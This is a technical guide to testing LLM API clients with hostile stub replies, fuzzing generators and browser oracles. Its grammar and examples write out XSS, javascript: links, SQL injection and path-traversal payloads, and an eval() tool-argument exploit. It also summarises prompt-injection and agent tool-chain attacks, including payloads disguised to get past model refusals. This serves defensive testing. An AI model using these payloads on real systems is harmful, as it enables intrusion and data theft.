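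The tester should vary where the stub splits the stream, for example in the middle of an HTML tag, between an escape character and the bracket after it, or partway through an order number. A partial order number can be serious because some clients close the brackets on unfinished JSON to show progress. If the stream stops after `{"order_id": "118`, such a client may end up with a valid request for order 118, which belongs to somebody else. The client should run a tool call only after the stream has finished properly.

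Network packets can also split an event, so the client may receive half a `data:` line. Vendor libraries normally handle this. A client that reads the stream with its own code needs a test for this, which a fake object can't provide.

MockServer splits text into pieces smaller than a word by default, and lets the tester set the delay before the first piece, the speed and the variation between pieces. CopilotKit's mock server, aimock, can end a stream early. The *write fixtures* guide on skills.sh shows the two settings for this. `truncateAfterChunks: 3` stops the reply after three pieces, and `disconnectAfterMs: 500` stops it after half a second.

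### Identifiers and finish reasons that do not match

After running a tool, the client sends the result in its next request, along with the call's identifier. The stub's log should show each result next to the call that produced it. A hostile stub can give two calls the same identifier. If the client stores results by identifier, the second result may overwrite the first, and the model may then describe one order using the details of another.

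The stub can send finish reasons that contradict the rest of the reply, such as `stop` with a tool call, `length` with a complete text, or `tool_calls` with an empty message. A client that checks only the finish reason may ignore a tool call, while one that checks only the `tool_calls` field will run it. Neither behaviour is necessarily a security bug, but if the shop's client logs according to the finish reason and acts on the `tool_calls` field, it could run a tool call that never appears in its log.

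Some mock servers correct such contradictions. MockServer changes the finish reason to `tool_calls` when the tester configures a tool call and marks tool use as required. This helps in ordinary tests, but a tester who wants the contradiction has to leave the required setting off or write the raw reply. CopilotKit's *aimock* lists overrides for the reply's `id`, `model`, `usage` and finish reason, which makes it well suited to testing hostile metadata.

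### Errors, delays and broken connections

The client also has to handle a server that fails:

| Fault | What the stub does | What can go wrong in the client |
|---|---|---|
| Rate limit | Returns status 429 with a `Retry-After` header | It waits for a week because the header asks it to |
| Temporary failure | Returns status 503 twice, then a normal reply | It restarts the whole task and runs the same tool call again |
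| Endless reply | Sends one short piece every few seconds | Its timeout restarts with each piece and never ends the request |
| Broken connection | Closes the connection in the middle of a reply | It saves half a summary as if it were complete |
| Wrong format | Returns an HTML error page with status 200 | It shows the page to the customer |

The second row does little harm with `find_order`, which only reads. With a refund tool, the shop would pay twice.

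Vendor libraries often retry failed requests automatically, so the stub's log may show three requests when the client's code made only one. The developer needs to know which layer is retrying before changing anything. Retries at several layers multiply, so if the library makes three attempts per call and the client calls it three times, a failing server receives nine requests.

MockServer's *AI MCP tools* lists settings for most of these faults, including errors with a `Retry-After` value, dropped connections, truncated bodies, broken JSON and replies that arrive a few bytes at a time. It also has a scenario in which the first few requests fail and the next one succeeds. Despite its name, aimock's `dropRate` returns a 500 error, and the setting that breaks the connection is `disconnectRate`. Both tools can apply faults at random, but a permanent test should specify exactly which request fails,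 because a fault that occurs in 30% of runs may not occur in the run where it would have exposed a bug.

### Pointing the client at the stub

Most clients have a base address setting, to which the vendor library adds the path for each request. For clients that use OpenAI's library, two environment variables are often enough:

```bash
OPENAI_BASE_URL=http://localhost:1080/v1 OPENAI_API_KEY=test-key pytest tests/
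```

OpenAI Mock API's *Introduction* shows the same change in code, setting `baseURL` to an address on the developer's own computer and the key to `test-key`. The library usually reads the variable once, when the program creates its API client, so a test that sets it afterwards has no effect.

The form of the address varies by provider. According to GitHub's *Supported providers*, a configuration guide for its software kit, an OpenAI address should include the full path, while an Azure address should contain only the host name. The guide also describes a setting for choosing between the chat completion and Responses formats. If the stub receives a request for a path it doesn't recognize, the tester should check the address and the format setting first.

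For frameworks with no base address setting, MockServer's *AI agent frameworks* recommends using the `HTTPS_PROXY` variable to send all of the program's traffic through MockServer. The client must then trust a certificate that MockServer generates. The tester should install this certificate only in the test environment, since anyone with the matching private key could read encrypted traffic from a computer that trusts it.

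The test also needs fake credentials. If a request reaches the real API by mistake, the provider will reject it, and the tester will see an error instead of a plausible answer. The tests also try to make the client misbehave, and it may leak whatever secrets it holds. Willison (2023) describes someone using prompt injection to read the secret OpenAI key of a well-known GPT-3 application. The shop's tester should therefore replace the database password and the chat bot's token as well as the model key.

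The test environment should run on an isolated network that can reach only the stub, the scratch database and the tester's canary server. Otherwise a hostile reply could make the client post in the real staff channel or send requests to a stranger's website. The firewall should log blocked connections, because an attempt to reach an outside address may itself be the bug. The stub should accept connections only from the test environment. Docker's usual `-p 1080:1080` option makes a server reachable from other computers unless the tester changes it to `-p 127.0.0.1:1080:1080`.

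### Galloway's demonstration

Garrett Galloway's demonstration, whose calculator client appeared in the discussion of grammars, is a complete stub test in two short Python programs. ctrlaidel explains how they work:

1. The server, `mal_serve.py`, imitates OpenAI's API. A variable named `CALC_ARGS` first contains the expression `2+2`. The next assignment replaces it with `open('pwned.txt', 'w').write('owned')`.
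2. The client, `dumb_client.py`, sends a request without any tools. The server answers with an ordinary chat message.
3. The client registers a tool named `use_calculator`, which takes one string called `expression`, and asks what 2 + 2 is.
4. The server sees that the request includes a tool. It returns a `function_call` with the name of the first tool and the contents of `CALC_ARGS`, whatever the user asked.
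5. The client parses the arguments with `json.loads` and passes the expression to `eval()`.
6. Python creates the file `pwned.txt`, containing the word "owned".

Every check before the last step succeeds. The arguments are valid JSON, the tool exists, and the expression is a string, as the schema requires. The calculator returns 5, because Python's `write` returns the number of characters written. A test that checked only whether the tool returned a number would pass, so the tester has to look for the file.

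The harmless first value of `CALC_ARGS`, `2+2`, is a control, and the client should return 4. If it doesn't, the client and server are not communicating properly, and the absence of a file in the hostile run would prove nothing. After replacing `eval()`, the developer should test both values again.

ctrlaidel calls the client typical of many production integrations but gives no examples. Galloway wrote it to be vulnerable, so the demonstration shows how the bug works and leaves open how common it is.

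The server would need two changes before it could test a modern agent. It returns tool calls in `function_call`, an older field that OpenAI has replaced with `tool_calls`, so a client that reads only the new field would ignore the payload and appear safe. The server also returns a tool call every time the request includes tools. `dumb_client.py` stops after one call, but an agent that sends the result back would receive the same call again and repeat this until it reached a limit. This is a good test of the limit, but it prevents the tester from seeing how the agent uses the result.

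### Mocking at BMW

*Automated structural testing of LLM-based agents*, written by engineers at BMW and AWS and published in January 2026, describes a more elaborate use of mocks. Its mock is an object that has the same interface as the model and replaces it inside the program. The test sets what the mock returns, then checks the agent's actions in a trace, which is a record of every model call and tool call.

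The first case study is a prototype assistant for drivers. One test concerns a customer who needs winter tyres:

1. The mock supplies the beginning of the conversation through a function called `add_output`. It offers to diagnose the car, calls the tools that fetch the vehicle's status and the customer's details, and reports that everything is fine.
2. The customer asks for winter tyres and suggests next Monday.
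3. The test calls `add_real_response`, which passes the next requests to a real model.
4. The test checks the trace for a call that lists appointments and another that books the expected one. It doesn't check the assistant's wording.

The scripted beginning brings the agent to the same point every time, and the live model then has to complete the booking. A security tester could instead have the mock put a hostile summary into the conversation at the second turn, then check whether the live model's later replies spread it. The live part of the test would not be repeatable and would need a real API key.

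The second case study is an agent that helps engineers find the causes of cloud failures. The engineers testing it mocked the results of its tools. To simulate a fault such as a deleted firewall rule, they wrote the logs it would produce instead of building a cloud account with that fault. They then checked whether the agent found the cause. They also checked that it looked at the system's architecture before reading error logs, because many AWS services produce similar errors.

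The paper treats injection as something to test for in the user's input. It shows that mocking a model is practical, but all the scripted replies in its code examples are ordinary, so they don't test output injection. Its driver assistant reached 96% test coverage, a measure of how much of the code ran during the tests. That would not reassure a security tester, because the line in `find_order` that pastes an order number into SQL counts as covered after one test with `1182`.

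According to the paper, a test that mocks every component reveals little about how they interact. In a security test, the sinks have to be real. The shop's tester needs an actual browser, terminal and scratch database, because whether a reply is dangerous depends on how those programs handle it.

### What existing tools can send

Several frameworks now include fake models. Their documentation shows scripted answers, tool calls and sometimes errors, but no hostile replies. Most of these fakes can return a hostile reply if the tester writes one.

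Pydantic AI, a Python framework, has two stub models, `TestModel` and `FunctionModel`. `TestModel` calls every tool, and Pydantic describes it as ordinary code that tries to satisfy each tool's schema, so it will rarely send anything the client should reject. In the documentation's weather example, it always supplies the date 1 January 2024, so the code for future dates never runs. `FunctionModel` calls a function that the tester writes, which can return any text or tool call. It needs a second function for streaming, and Pydantic notes that some agents stream their requests even when the developer calls a non-streaming method.

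AI SDK gives testers more control than LangChain's fakes do. Its `MockLanguageModelV4` takes a tool call's arguments as a string, so the toolkit still has to parse them. The tester also decides where each streamed piece ends. Temporal, which makes software for long-running programs, offers a fake model for OpenAI's Agents SDK that returns replies from a list but doesn't implement the streaming method.

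Mock servers are closer to what a hostile test needs. MockServer is the only tool here with a dedicated function for returning hostile or malformed replies, `mock_adversarial_llm_response`. llmposter, written in Rust, returns prepared replies in the OpenAI, Anthropic and Gemini formats. aimock can garble JSON and break streams, but the tester has to write any hostile text.

Unlike all of these, Microsoft's Dev Proxy simulates model failures by adding an instruction to the request, telling the real model to write a bad answer (Microsoft, 2025). Microsoft added this feature and token-based rate limits in August 2025. The failure plugin offers 15 kinds of bad answer, including invented facts, bias and the wrong format. The result varies between runs, and the model may refuse to write something dangerous. The plugin is therefore better for testing how people cope with poor answers than for testing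 a sink.

| Tool | Where it cuts | Hostile replies |
|---|---|---|
| LangChain's fake models | Object | The tester can script text and parsed tool calls |
| Pydantic AI's `TestModel` | Object | No, it aims for valid values |
| Pydantic AI's `FunctionModel` | Object | The tester's function can return them |
| AI SDK's `MockLanguageModelV4` | Object | The tester can script them, including broken arguments |
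| Temporal's fake model | Object | The tester can script them, without streaming |
| MockServer | Server or proxy | Built in |
| aimock | Server | Built-in format faults; the tester writes the text |
| Dev Proxy | Proxy | Poor answers from a real model |

### When the stub is wrong

A stub can become outdated when the provider adds fields, renames them or changes their types. Tests can then pass while the live client fails, or the client can ignore a hostile reply because it no longer reads the field containing it. Comparing the stub with the real API reveals most such changes. MockServer's *Mock Drift Detection* gives the example of a stub that returns the number `7` as an identifier when the real API returns the string `"7"`. This comparison checks field names and types, not values, so it would miss a new finish reason if the old and new values are both strings. aimock's developers run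 a daily check against real APIs. Such checks need a real key, so they should run separately from the hostile tests.

A stub's replies can also be too simple. They may always contain one short English text or one tool call, while real replies include empty pieces, several calls at once, unfamiliar fields and text in other scripts. The usual sign of this problem is a production failure that the team can't reproduce with any stub reply. Recording real traffic helps, but by default MockServer merges duplicate recordings and generalises values that vary. Testers who want the original traffic should turn this off but still let MockServer remove secrets. TanStack, which makes a toolkit for AI applications, treats its prepared replies as "the source of truth" when behaviour is unclear. This is convenient for contributors, but any mistake in a prepared reply then becomes part of the standard for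 the code.

Some fakes hide extra requests. LangChain's `FakeListChatModel` restarts its list when it runs out, and AI SDK's `mockValues` helper repeats the last value, so a client stuck in a loop may keep getting sensible replies. `fakeModel` raises an error instead. With the other two, the test should check the number of calls.

The hardest failure to notice is an application that still calls a real API during the test. The application may have created its API client before the test changed the address. It may have a second connection for another task, such as moderation, that ignores the setting. Or it may switch to a backup provider when the stub returns an error, so that the test of error handling sends a request to a real model. In each case, the test can pass because the answer looks normal.

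You can see this in the stub's log, which contains fewer requests than the client made. A unique marker in every stubbed reply also helps, because any answer on the shop's chat page without the marker came from somewhere else. Fake keys and the isolated network turn most of these mistakes into visible errors. Pydantic AI can also block real requests with `ALLOW_MODEL_REQUESTS=False`, but the setting doesn't cover code that calls a provider outside the framework.

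Mock servers can themselves cause the leak. In SPY mode, MockServer sends the real service any request that matches no prepared reply. Its default mode, SIMULATE, returns a 404 error instead. aimock has a strict mode for unmatched requests, but according to a later copy of its documentation on Ecosyste.ms, a header can override that mode for a single request. Before the first hostile test, the tester should send an unmatched request and confirm that the request fails.

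## Generating hostile and random responses

The shop's stub picks its answers from `REPLIES`, a list of texts and tool calls. A generator is a program that fills that list. The table lists five kinds of generator in order of effort. Most clients need more than one, because each misses bugs that another finds.

| Generator | What the tester needs | Bugs it finds | Bugs it misses |
|---|---|---|---|
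| Random characters | A few lines of code | Crashes, encoding faults, unfiltered control characters | Anything that depends on a particular word or structure |
| Mutated recordings | Real replies | Faults in parsing, joining pieces and reading metadata | Attacks that look nothing like an ordinary reply |
| Payload lists | Known attacks for each sink | Familiar kinds of output injection | New variants, and payloads that work only inside certain markup |
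| Grammar | Rules for Markdown, JSON or SQL | Output injection in unusual positions | Whatever the rules leave out, and bugs that need several turns |
| Sequences of tool calls | A map of the tools and the data they share | Checks that lapse after the first call, payloads stored for later | Sequences that nobody thought to model |

### Random characters

Miller and colleagues built the first fuzzer in 1990. *Large Language Models Based Fuzzing Techniques* (Huang, Zhao and colleagues, 2024) describes most fuzzers before 2005 as random and using no information about the program under test. Testing with random text still takes the least effort. The stub should put the text in the reply's `content` field and let a JSON library encode it. If the stub fills the whole HTTP body with random bytes, the vendor library will reject nearly every reply, and the client's own code will hardly run.

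Suppose each reply has 1,000 characters, each picked uniformly at random from code points 0 to 255. The chance that a reply contains no backspace is (255/256)^1000, or about 2%, so about 98% of replies contain at least one. The same is true of any other single control character. A staff terminal tool with no filter would fail almost at once.

Pairs are rarer. For the escape character followed by `[`, which opens a terminal escape sequence, the chance is:

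```text
places where the pair can start:   1,000 - 1 = 999
chance at each place:              1/256 × 1/256 = 1/65,536
expected number per reply:         999 / 65,536 ≈ 0.0152
chance of at least one:            1 - e^(-0.0152) ≈ 1.5%
```

The chance of missing the pair in all n replies is (1 - 0.0151)^n, which falls to 5% at n ≈ 197. The tester therefore needs about 200 replies for a 95% chance of seeing the pair, and a local stub can send them quickly.

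Longer strings are out of reach. Suppose the generator now uses only the 95 printable characters, and the tester is waiting for the seven characters `<script`:

```text
places where the string can start:   1,000 - 6 = 994
chance at each place:                1/95^7 ≈ 1 in 70 trillion
expected number per reply:           994 / 95^7 ≈ 1 in 70 billion
```

At 1,000 replies a second, those seven characters would take more than two years to appear, on average. They are only the start of an element, and each further character that has to be right multiplies the wait by 95.

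### Mutated recordings

A mutation fuzzer makes small changes to a good input. In a talk published by It Will Never Work in Theory (2023), the researcher Marcel Böhme gave an example of how many attempts this can save. Suppose a program fails only on the input `bad!`. Random bytes have to match all four characters, which takes 256^4, or about four billion, attempts on average. A fuzzer that starts from `bad?` only has to pick the last character (a 1 in 4 chance) and change it to an exclamation mark (1 in 256), which takes about 1,000 attempts on average. Böhme acknowledged that he had made the example easier by choosing such a good starting point.

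Recordings of real replies give the shop good starting points, but how the tester changes them matters too. If the tester wants order 1182 to become order 1183, replacing one random character in a 400-character reply does this once in 400 × 95 = 38,000 attempts on average. A generator that parses the reply first and replaces one random digit of the order number does it once in 4 × 10 = 40. Other useful changes to a parsed reply are deleting a field, turning a number into a string, repeating a tool call and cutting the text short. The tester should also keep some blind byte changes, since a broken connection can leave invalid JSON.

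Starting from recordings also guards against misunderstanding the format. tuochat's *API Streaming Learnings* describes a chat client whose tests used invented stream chunks, each repeating all the text so far. The tests passed, but the live service sent only the new text in each chunk. The client treated these chunks as cumulative, so it cut off valid characters and joined the rest incorrectly.

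Damaged replies mostly expose crashes and exceptions. *LLM-Assisted Model-Based Fuzzing of Protocol Implementations* (2025) acknowledges this limitation in its own method and says many fuzzers share it. The shop's client doesn't crash when it shows a customer someone else's order. Mutation may well produce another customer's order number, such as 1183, but the test will catch the bug only if it checks whose order came back.

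### Payload lists

With a payload list, the tester sends known attacks instead of searching for them. Each sink gets its own list: an image with an error handler for the chat page, `@everyone` for the notifier, a carriage return for the terminal. The generator then puts every payload in every field that the threat model marks as open to an attacker, including function names, arguments and, if a router might be hostile, metadata. Thirty payloads in ten fields make only 300 replies, so the whole list can run after each code change. Putting terminal payloads in the chat page's replies takes little extra work and sometimes finds a flaw, because text often reaches more sinks than the map shows.

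A list contains only the spellings its author knew. *Evolutionary Multi-Task Injection Testing on Web Application Firewalls* (2022) tested filters that block suspicious web requests, using a separate grammar to create variants of each type of injection. One example writes `src` as `%53r%43`, which decodes to `SrC`. A filter that searches only for the lower-case word would let it through.

Some gaps are harder to fill by adding spellings. A sanitizer on the server has to predict how the browser will parse a piece of HTML. *Parse Me, Baby, One More Time* (2024) shows that the two can disagree and calls these disagreements parsing differentials. An attacker can exploit one by writing markup that is harmless as the sanitizer parses it but dangerous as the browser does. A list of ordinary script elements might never trigger such a difference, but a generator that nests and breaks tags in many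 ways has some chance of finding one.

### A grammar for the shop

A grammar is a set of rules for building text. In *Fuzzing with Grammars*, a chapter of the online textbook *The Fuzzing Book*, each symbol in angle brackets has a list of possible replacements. The generator begins with a start symbol and replaces symbols at random until only text remains.

For web requests, according to *Fuzzing Frameworks for Server-side Web Applications* (2024), the fuzzer copies some parts unchanged and fills the others from a source such as a dictionary. The shop can do the same with replies, using Markdown and JSON as the fixed parts and its payload lists as the dictionary. This grammar covers the web chat page and `find_order`:

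```text
<reply>   ::= <page> | <lookup>

<page>    ::= <before> <item> <after>
<before>  ::= "" | "Your order is on its way. " | "- " | "> "
<item>    ::= <html> | "**" <html> "**" | "`" <html> "`"
            | "[" <html> "](/orders/1182)"
            | "[Track it](" <url> ")" | "![Photo](" <url> ")"
<after>   ::= "" | "\n\nAnything else?"
<html>    ::= "canary-a17" | "<b>canary-a17</b>"
            | "<img src='/missing-a17.png' onerror=\"document.title='canary-a17'\">"
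<url>     ::= "/orders/1182" | "https://canary.example/a17.png"
            | "javascript:document.title='canary-a17'"

<lookup>  ::= {"order_id": json(<id> <tail>)}
<id>      ::= "" | "1182" | "1183"
<tail>    ::= "" | "'" | "' OR '1'='1" | " OR 1=1"
```

The rules for `<page>` put the same payload in a plain sentence, a list item, a quotation, bold text, code and the text of a link, because a renderer may escape HTML in one of these places but not in another. In the lookups, a lone quotation mark will usually cause an SQL error if the client pastes the value into its query, and ` OR 1=1` tests a client that writes the number without quotation marks. The `json()` step encodes the finished value. Without it, the first payload containing a double quotation mark would break the JSON, and the client would reject the reply before the value reached the database.

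These rules produce 144 pages and 12 lookups, few enough that a test can send them all. If the generator chooses at random instead, the image with the error handler appears in 1/2 × 4/6 × 1/3 of the replies, or one in nine. Random printable characters would take more than two years to produce just the seven characters of `<script`.

*Building Fast Fuzzers* (2019) explains that grammars work well because their output gets past the checks that reject random input, so more of it exercises the code behind them. LangFuzz, a grammar fuzzer that also reuses fragments of existing programs, found more than 2,600 bugs in JavaScript interpreters. The same paper notes the obvious drawback that somebody has to write the grammar first.

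Software can now do some of that work. *Toward Inferring Accurate Context-free Grammars for Big Languages in a Black-box Setting* (2026) presents XVADA, a program that learns a grammar by observing which inputs a parser accepts and rejects. Its developers tried it on the Python version of Liquid, Shopify's template language. A fuzzer using the learned grammar found five bugs, but the most serious flaw, CVE-2026-55865, appeared earlier, while XVADA was still trying out inputs. A malformed `case` tag with no closing `endcase` sent the parser into an infinite loop.

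A grammar that generates only complete, valid templates would never have produced that input. The shop's generator should therefore damage some of its replies by removing one closing tag, bracket or quotation mark.

### Tool calls over several turns

The grammar above generates one reply at a time. *FuzzySQL* (2026), a study of database testing, observes that many grammar fuzzers struggle when one statement depends on another or on the current state of the system, so it has a language model fill in the grammar's templates. The same problem arises when testing clients that run tool calls. Suppose the shop's client checks at the first lookup that the order belongs to the customer, then treats the whole conversation as approved. A single request for order 1183, which belongs to someone else, fails as it should. A request for the customer's own order, 1182, followed by one for 1183 reveals the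 bug.

The best evidence that such bugs are common comes from *ChainFuzzer* (Wu, Nan and colleagues, 2026), which tested 20 open-source agent programs with 998 tools in total and confirmed 365 vulnerabilities, 302 of which needed more than one tool. In its main example, an agent looks for a software patch, downloads it, saves it to a file and runs the file. Together these steps let a stranger's web page run code, but each is reasonable on its own, so testing the tools one at a time would not reveal the problem.

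The number of possible call sequences grows too fast with length to try them all. With the shop's 12 lookups, there are 144 sequences of two calls and 248,832 of five. ChainFuzzer narrows the search by working backwards. It finds the tools whose inputs can affect a dangerous function such as `exec`, then looks for other tools that could supply those inputs, either directly or through a shared file or database. The shop's tester can do this by hand using the threat model's map.

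Wu and colleagues used live models and spent much of their effort getting them to produce the responses the attacks needed. Their first prompts led the agent through the intended chain in only 27% of cases, and refining the prompts raised this to 95%. The models also refused or weakened many payloads, and only 18% took effect before the researchers disguised them. A stub removes both obstacles, but the tester still has to check whether a live model could produce the same sequence.

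A scripted sequence should sometimes copy text from the client's last request into the next reply, as a real model would. To test the shop's stored tickets, for example, the stub writes the marker `canary-a17` into one test customer's ticket summary. A different test customer then asks about the same product. If the resulting request to the stub contains the marker, the stub repeats it in its answer, wrapped in HTML. This shows whether stored text from one customer can influence another's request, and whether the second customer's page treats the answer as safe because it began as the shop's own data.

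### Payloads split across streamed pieces

When the client streams, the generator must also choose where to cut the reply. A 200-character reply has 199 gaps between characters, and a 10-character pattern has 9 gaps inside it, so one random cut has a 9 in 199 (4.5%) chance of splitting the pattern. At that rate, a 95% chance of splitting it at least once takes about 65 replies. The two characters that open a terminal escape sequence have only one gap between them, so a random cut has a 1 in 199 chance of splitting them.

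Placing cuts deliberately takes far fewer replies than placing them at random. Nine replies cover every position for a single cut inside the 10-character pattern, and 2^9 = 512 cover every combination of cuts. TanStack's *AI Streaming*, the guide to a Markdown library, describes an even more thorough practice in which the developers compare the library's two renderers at every character boundary of their sample texts, including raw HTML and executable links.

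A stub that sends four characters at a time will always split a 10-character pattern, but in the same places on every run, so it misses the other split positions. The tester can cover those by adding one, two and then three characters in front of the payload.

Splitting a payload across streamed chunks matters because some clients filter each chunk separately. Chrome for Developers' *Best practices to render streamed LLM responses* (2025) recommends sanitizing the combined text, but its sample code does so before converting the Markdown, so a `javascript:` link might still get through unless the Markdown parser blocks it. In a newer guide from the same site, Nalpas (2026) converts the Markdown first and then sanitizes the result. The streaming tests should include a Markdown `javascript:` link as well as HTML.

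A client's own buffer can split streamed text in places where the network didn't. In March 2026, a user of the website system Drupal reported that its AI module was corrupting pages. The module collected streamed text and passed it on at every line break or after 100 characters. One image address came out as `/sites/default` and `/files/inline-images/image.png`, with the second half outside the tag. A maintainer could not reproduce the damage but added a fix and tests. The fix delays a split that would fall inside a quoted address beginning with `http` or a slash. It has no explicit rule for other attributes, such as a long image description, so a tester should try those too.

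The generator should also place payloads just before, across and just after every buffer boundary and length limit in the client's code. Netresearch's *ADR-088* (2026), a design record for AI software used with the website system TYPO3, describes a filter that masks secret keys in streamed replies. A filter that checked one piece at a time would miss a key split into `sk-abcdef012` and `3456789`, so the software holds back the last 128 bytes until more text arrives. An earlier design stopped filtering after 50 kilobytes and leaked any key beyond that point, a flaw that no short test reply could have revealed.

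Even widely used libraries can get the boundaries between pieces of a stream wrong. A February 2025 fix on GitHub corrected an off-by-one error in how OpenAI's own library read those pieces.

### When coverage feedback helps

A coverage-guided fuzzer records which branches of the client's code each input runs, and it keeps and further mutates every input that reaches a new branch. Suppose a client's filter looks for `<script` one character at a time. Each correct character reaches a new branch, so the fuzzer keeps each partial match. If it works on a seven-character string and always continues from its best attempt, the next correct character takes about 665 tries (7 positions × 95 printable characters), and the whole string takes about 4,700. Guessing all seven characters at once would take about 70 trillion.

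This works only if the client has such branches. Output injection often results from a missing check, so there is no branch for the fuzzer to discover. The shop's vulnerable chat page, for example, has no filter, so it runs the same code whether or not a response contains `<script`. The browser contains the code that recognises the tag, and the fuzzer normally doesn't measure that code.

Coverage feedback is more useful where the client does substantial parsing, for example in a hand-written event-stream reader, code that closes the brackets on unfinished JSON, or a filter for control characters. It can also guide grammar-based generation towards code that has not yet run. The Fuzzing Book's *Greybox Fuzzing with Grammars* explains this combination. A fuzzer of this type found the Liquid bugs, and template parsers are good targets for it.

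For a client that mostly passes text along, a coverage report is usually enough. The tester runs the ordinary generators once with a coverage tool, then reads the list of lines that never ran. Open WebUI's handler for `execute` events would have stood out in such a list, as would the code that handles a `content_filter` finish reason if no reply had used it.

Feedback can come from tool calls as well as code branches. *VeriGrey* (2026) tests agents with prompt injections and records the sequence of tool calls that follows each one. With a stub, the tester chooses which calls the reply requests and so already knows that sequence. It would be more informative to record which calls the client ran, refused or repeated.

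### Generators written by a coding agent

Writing good generators used to take a lot of manual work, which language models have reduced. Huang and colleagues describe an earlier tool, InputBlaster, that tests mobile apps with unusual text. Its developers thought asking a model for every input would be too slow and expensive, so they had the model write small generators instead. A 2026 study took this approach much further, examining whether such generators could make coverage guidance unnecessary.

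In *Fuzzing with Agents? Generators Are All You Need*, Vikram and Padhye (2026) gave a coding agent based on Claude Opus 4.5 the source code of seven Java programs, including a JSON parser, a JavaScript compiler and a file compressor. The agent had up to an hour per program to write an input generator, try it in two-minute runs and improve it. Two of the agent's three versions also received a report on which important branches their inputs had missed. Each version repeated the task five times.

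The baselines were generators that people had written for earlier research. Every generator then ran for three hours in two ways: with coverage-guided mutation, and with plain random choices. The main results were:

- **Coverage reached.** On four of the seven programs, at least one version of the agent reached significantly more branches than the human-written generator. On the bytecode library BCEL, all three reached 54% fewer.
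- **Value of coverage guidance.** It improved the human-written generators on all seven programs, by 40% on average. For the agent's generators, the average change lay between -0.1% and 2.0% and was never statistically significant.
- **Value of the branch reports.** They helped the agent improve its first draft in 74% of runs, but the final generators were about as good without them.
- **Cost.** One generator cost between $7.54 and $12.84 on average.

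These results do not fully support the subtitle. Some baselines were weak. The largest gain, 148%, was on the compressor, where the human-written generator produced only random bytes. Comparing the best of three agents with a single baseline also favours the agents. The study measured branch coverage rather than the number of bugs found. Vikram acknowledges that reaching more code does not guarantee finding more faults, and that the results may not extend beyond Java.

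The study did not include a client of a model API, but several of its lessons should carry over. For about ten dollars, a coding agent can read the shop's client, list the fields and event types it handles, and write a generator that covers them. That is probably a better use of time than setting up coverage guidance, especially since most of the client's code only passes text along.

BCEL includes functions for building valid files, and the human-written generator used them, but the agent overlooked them and wrote the bytes directly, so the parser rejected many of its files early. To avoid this, the shop should point its agent to recorded replies and the vendor library's data types. On the JavaScript compiler, the agent made its generator worse in three of five runs by having it produce simpler programs so that more would compile. A generator for hostile replies could go wrong in the same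 way if its author aims for replies that the client accepts. The shop should instruct its agent to generate valid replies containing harmful values, plus a fixed share of broken replies.

### When to stop

A payload list is finished once every payload has run in every field with every chosen cut. The shop's grammar is also small enough to test exhaustively. Random generators can run forever, so they need a stopping rule.

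Let p be the share of a generator's replies that would make the client fail. If the replies are independent, the chance that n of them all pass is (1 - p)^n. The tester looks for the largest p that would still give a clean run 5% of the time:

```text
(1 - p)^n = 0.05
n × ln(1 - p) = ln 0.05 ≈ -3
p ≈ 3/n        because ln(1 - p) ≈ -p when p is small
```

After 10,000 replies without a failure, the tester can say with 95% confidence that the failure probability p is below 3/10,000, or 0.03%. Medical researchers use the same rule for side effects not seen in a trial. *Systematic reviews of adverse effects* also advises them to ask how thoroughly anyone looked for those effects. The same question applies to an automatic check, which might miss a leak.

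The rule requires separate draws from an unchanged generator. Coverage-guided fuzzing breaks this condition because each new input depends on which code earlier inputs reached. A client that remembers previous conversations also breaks it, unless the tester resets the client between replies.

A different estimate uses coverage to judge whether more testing would reach anything new. The Fuzzing Book's *When To Stop Fuzzing* traces the idea to Alan Turing and I. J. Good, who needed to estimate the chance of events they had never observed while breaking the Enigma cipher. The older formula counts the pieces of code that exactly one input has run, and divides by the number of inputs. Lee and Böhme (2025), in *Dependency-aware Residual Risk Analysis*, point out that it can give absurd answers. In their example, the hundredth input enters a long stretch of new code, the count jumps to 1,021, and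 the estimate becomes 1,021/100 = 10.21, which can't be a probability. They count inputs instead:

```text
chance of reaching new code ≈ inputs that ran something no other input ran / all inputs
```

In the example, that is 3/100, or 3%. On eight real programs, the estimate's typical error was a fifth of the older formula's. Lee and Böhme treat the result as an upper limit on the chance that the next input reveals a new bug. That is reasonable for crashes in unexplored code but not for output injection, because a hostile order number can do harm in a line of code that has already handled thousands of ordinary ones. For the shop, the estimate can show that a generator has run out of new code to reach, but it can't show that the client is safe.

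Both calculations describe a single generator, and a different one can find many bugs that the first missed. Microsoft's *Equation of a Fuzzing Curve* gives the example of a sophisticated fuzzer that has run millions of times and seems to have found everything, until someone writes a new fuzzer in five lines of Python and finds many more bugs.

An attacker chooses replies deliberately, so a failure rate measured on random replies doesn't measure the risk of an attack. Suppose the shop's chat page runs any HTML it receives, and a tester sends it 10,000 replies of random printable characters. Very likely none of them runs a script, and the rule of three correctly puts the failure rate for such replies below 0.03%. But an attacker who can make the model return one image with an error handler succeeds every time. The test record should therefore give the failure rate together with the generator's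 name, version and seed. After a clean run of 10,000, adding one new payload or grammar rule is usually more useful than sending another 10,000 replies from the old generator.

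## Deciding whether a response did harm

Fuzzers normally report inputs that crash the program. This misses most output injections, because a successful one usually leaves the client running normally, as it did with Galloway's calculator. A well-defended client may look worse than a vulnerable one, since it might raise an exception when it rejects a bad order number.

In *ToFu*, Ananto, Prevost-Avenel and colleagues (2026) built a fuzzer for the tools that models call through MCP. They ran it on 273 servers and confirmed 253 bugs, including 64 path traversals and 3 command injections, none of which needed a crash to show up. In their standard example, a file tool that should stay inside its workspace opens `../../etc/passwd` and returns normally. A tester needs an oracle that checks for things the tool must never do to catch this.

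### An oracle for each sink

For the chat page, the oracle is a headless browser, which is a real browser that a program controls without opening a window. The test asks the assistant a question and records how the page reacts to the stub's reply:

```text
start recording every request the page makes
ask "Where is order 1182?"               (the stub sends the hostile reply)
wait 2 seconds                           (a broken image takes a moment to fail)
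if any request went to canary.example:   report "outside request"
click every link that starts with javascript:
if the page title is "canary-a17":       report "script ran"
```

The grammar's `javascript:` link needs `;0` added to the end of its code. Without it, `document.title='canary-a17'` returns a string, and browsers replace the whole page with any string that a `javascript:` link returns. The new page has no title, so the oracle would miss a script that had run. With `;0`, the link returns a number and the page stays in place.

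The browser's list may include requests that the CSP blocked, so the canary server's log is better evidence that data left the client. Each test reply should have its own address, such as `r4471-2.canary.example`, so that a visit identifies the reply even hours later. Putting the identifier in the host name also exposes leaks through DNS lookups, if the tester runs the domain's name server. The canary server must be public for the notifier test, because the chat platform fetches link previews from its own machines. Scanners probe public servers, so the oracle should count only visits to addresses it has issued.

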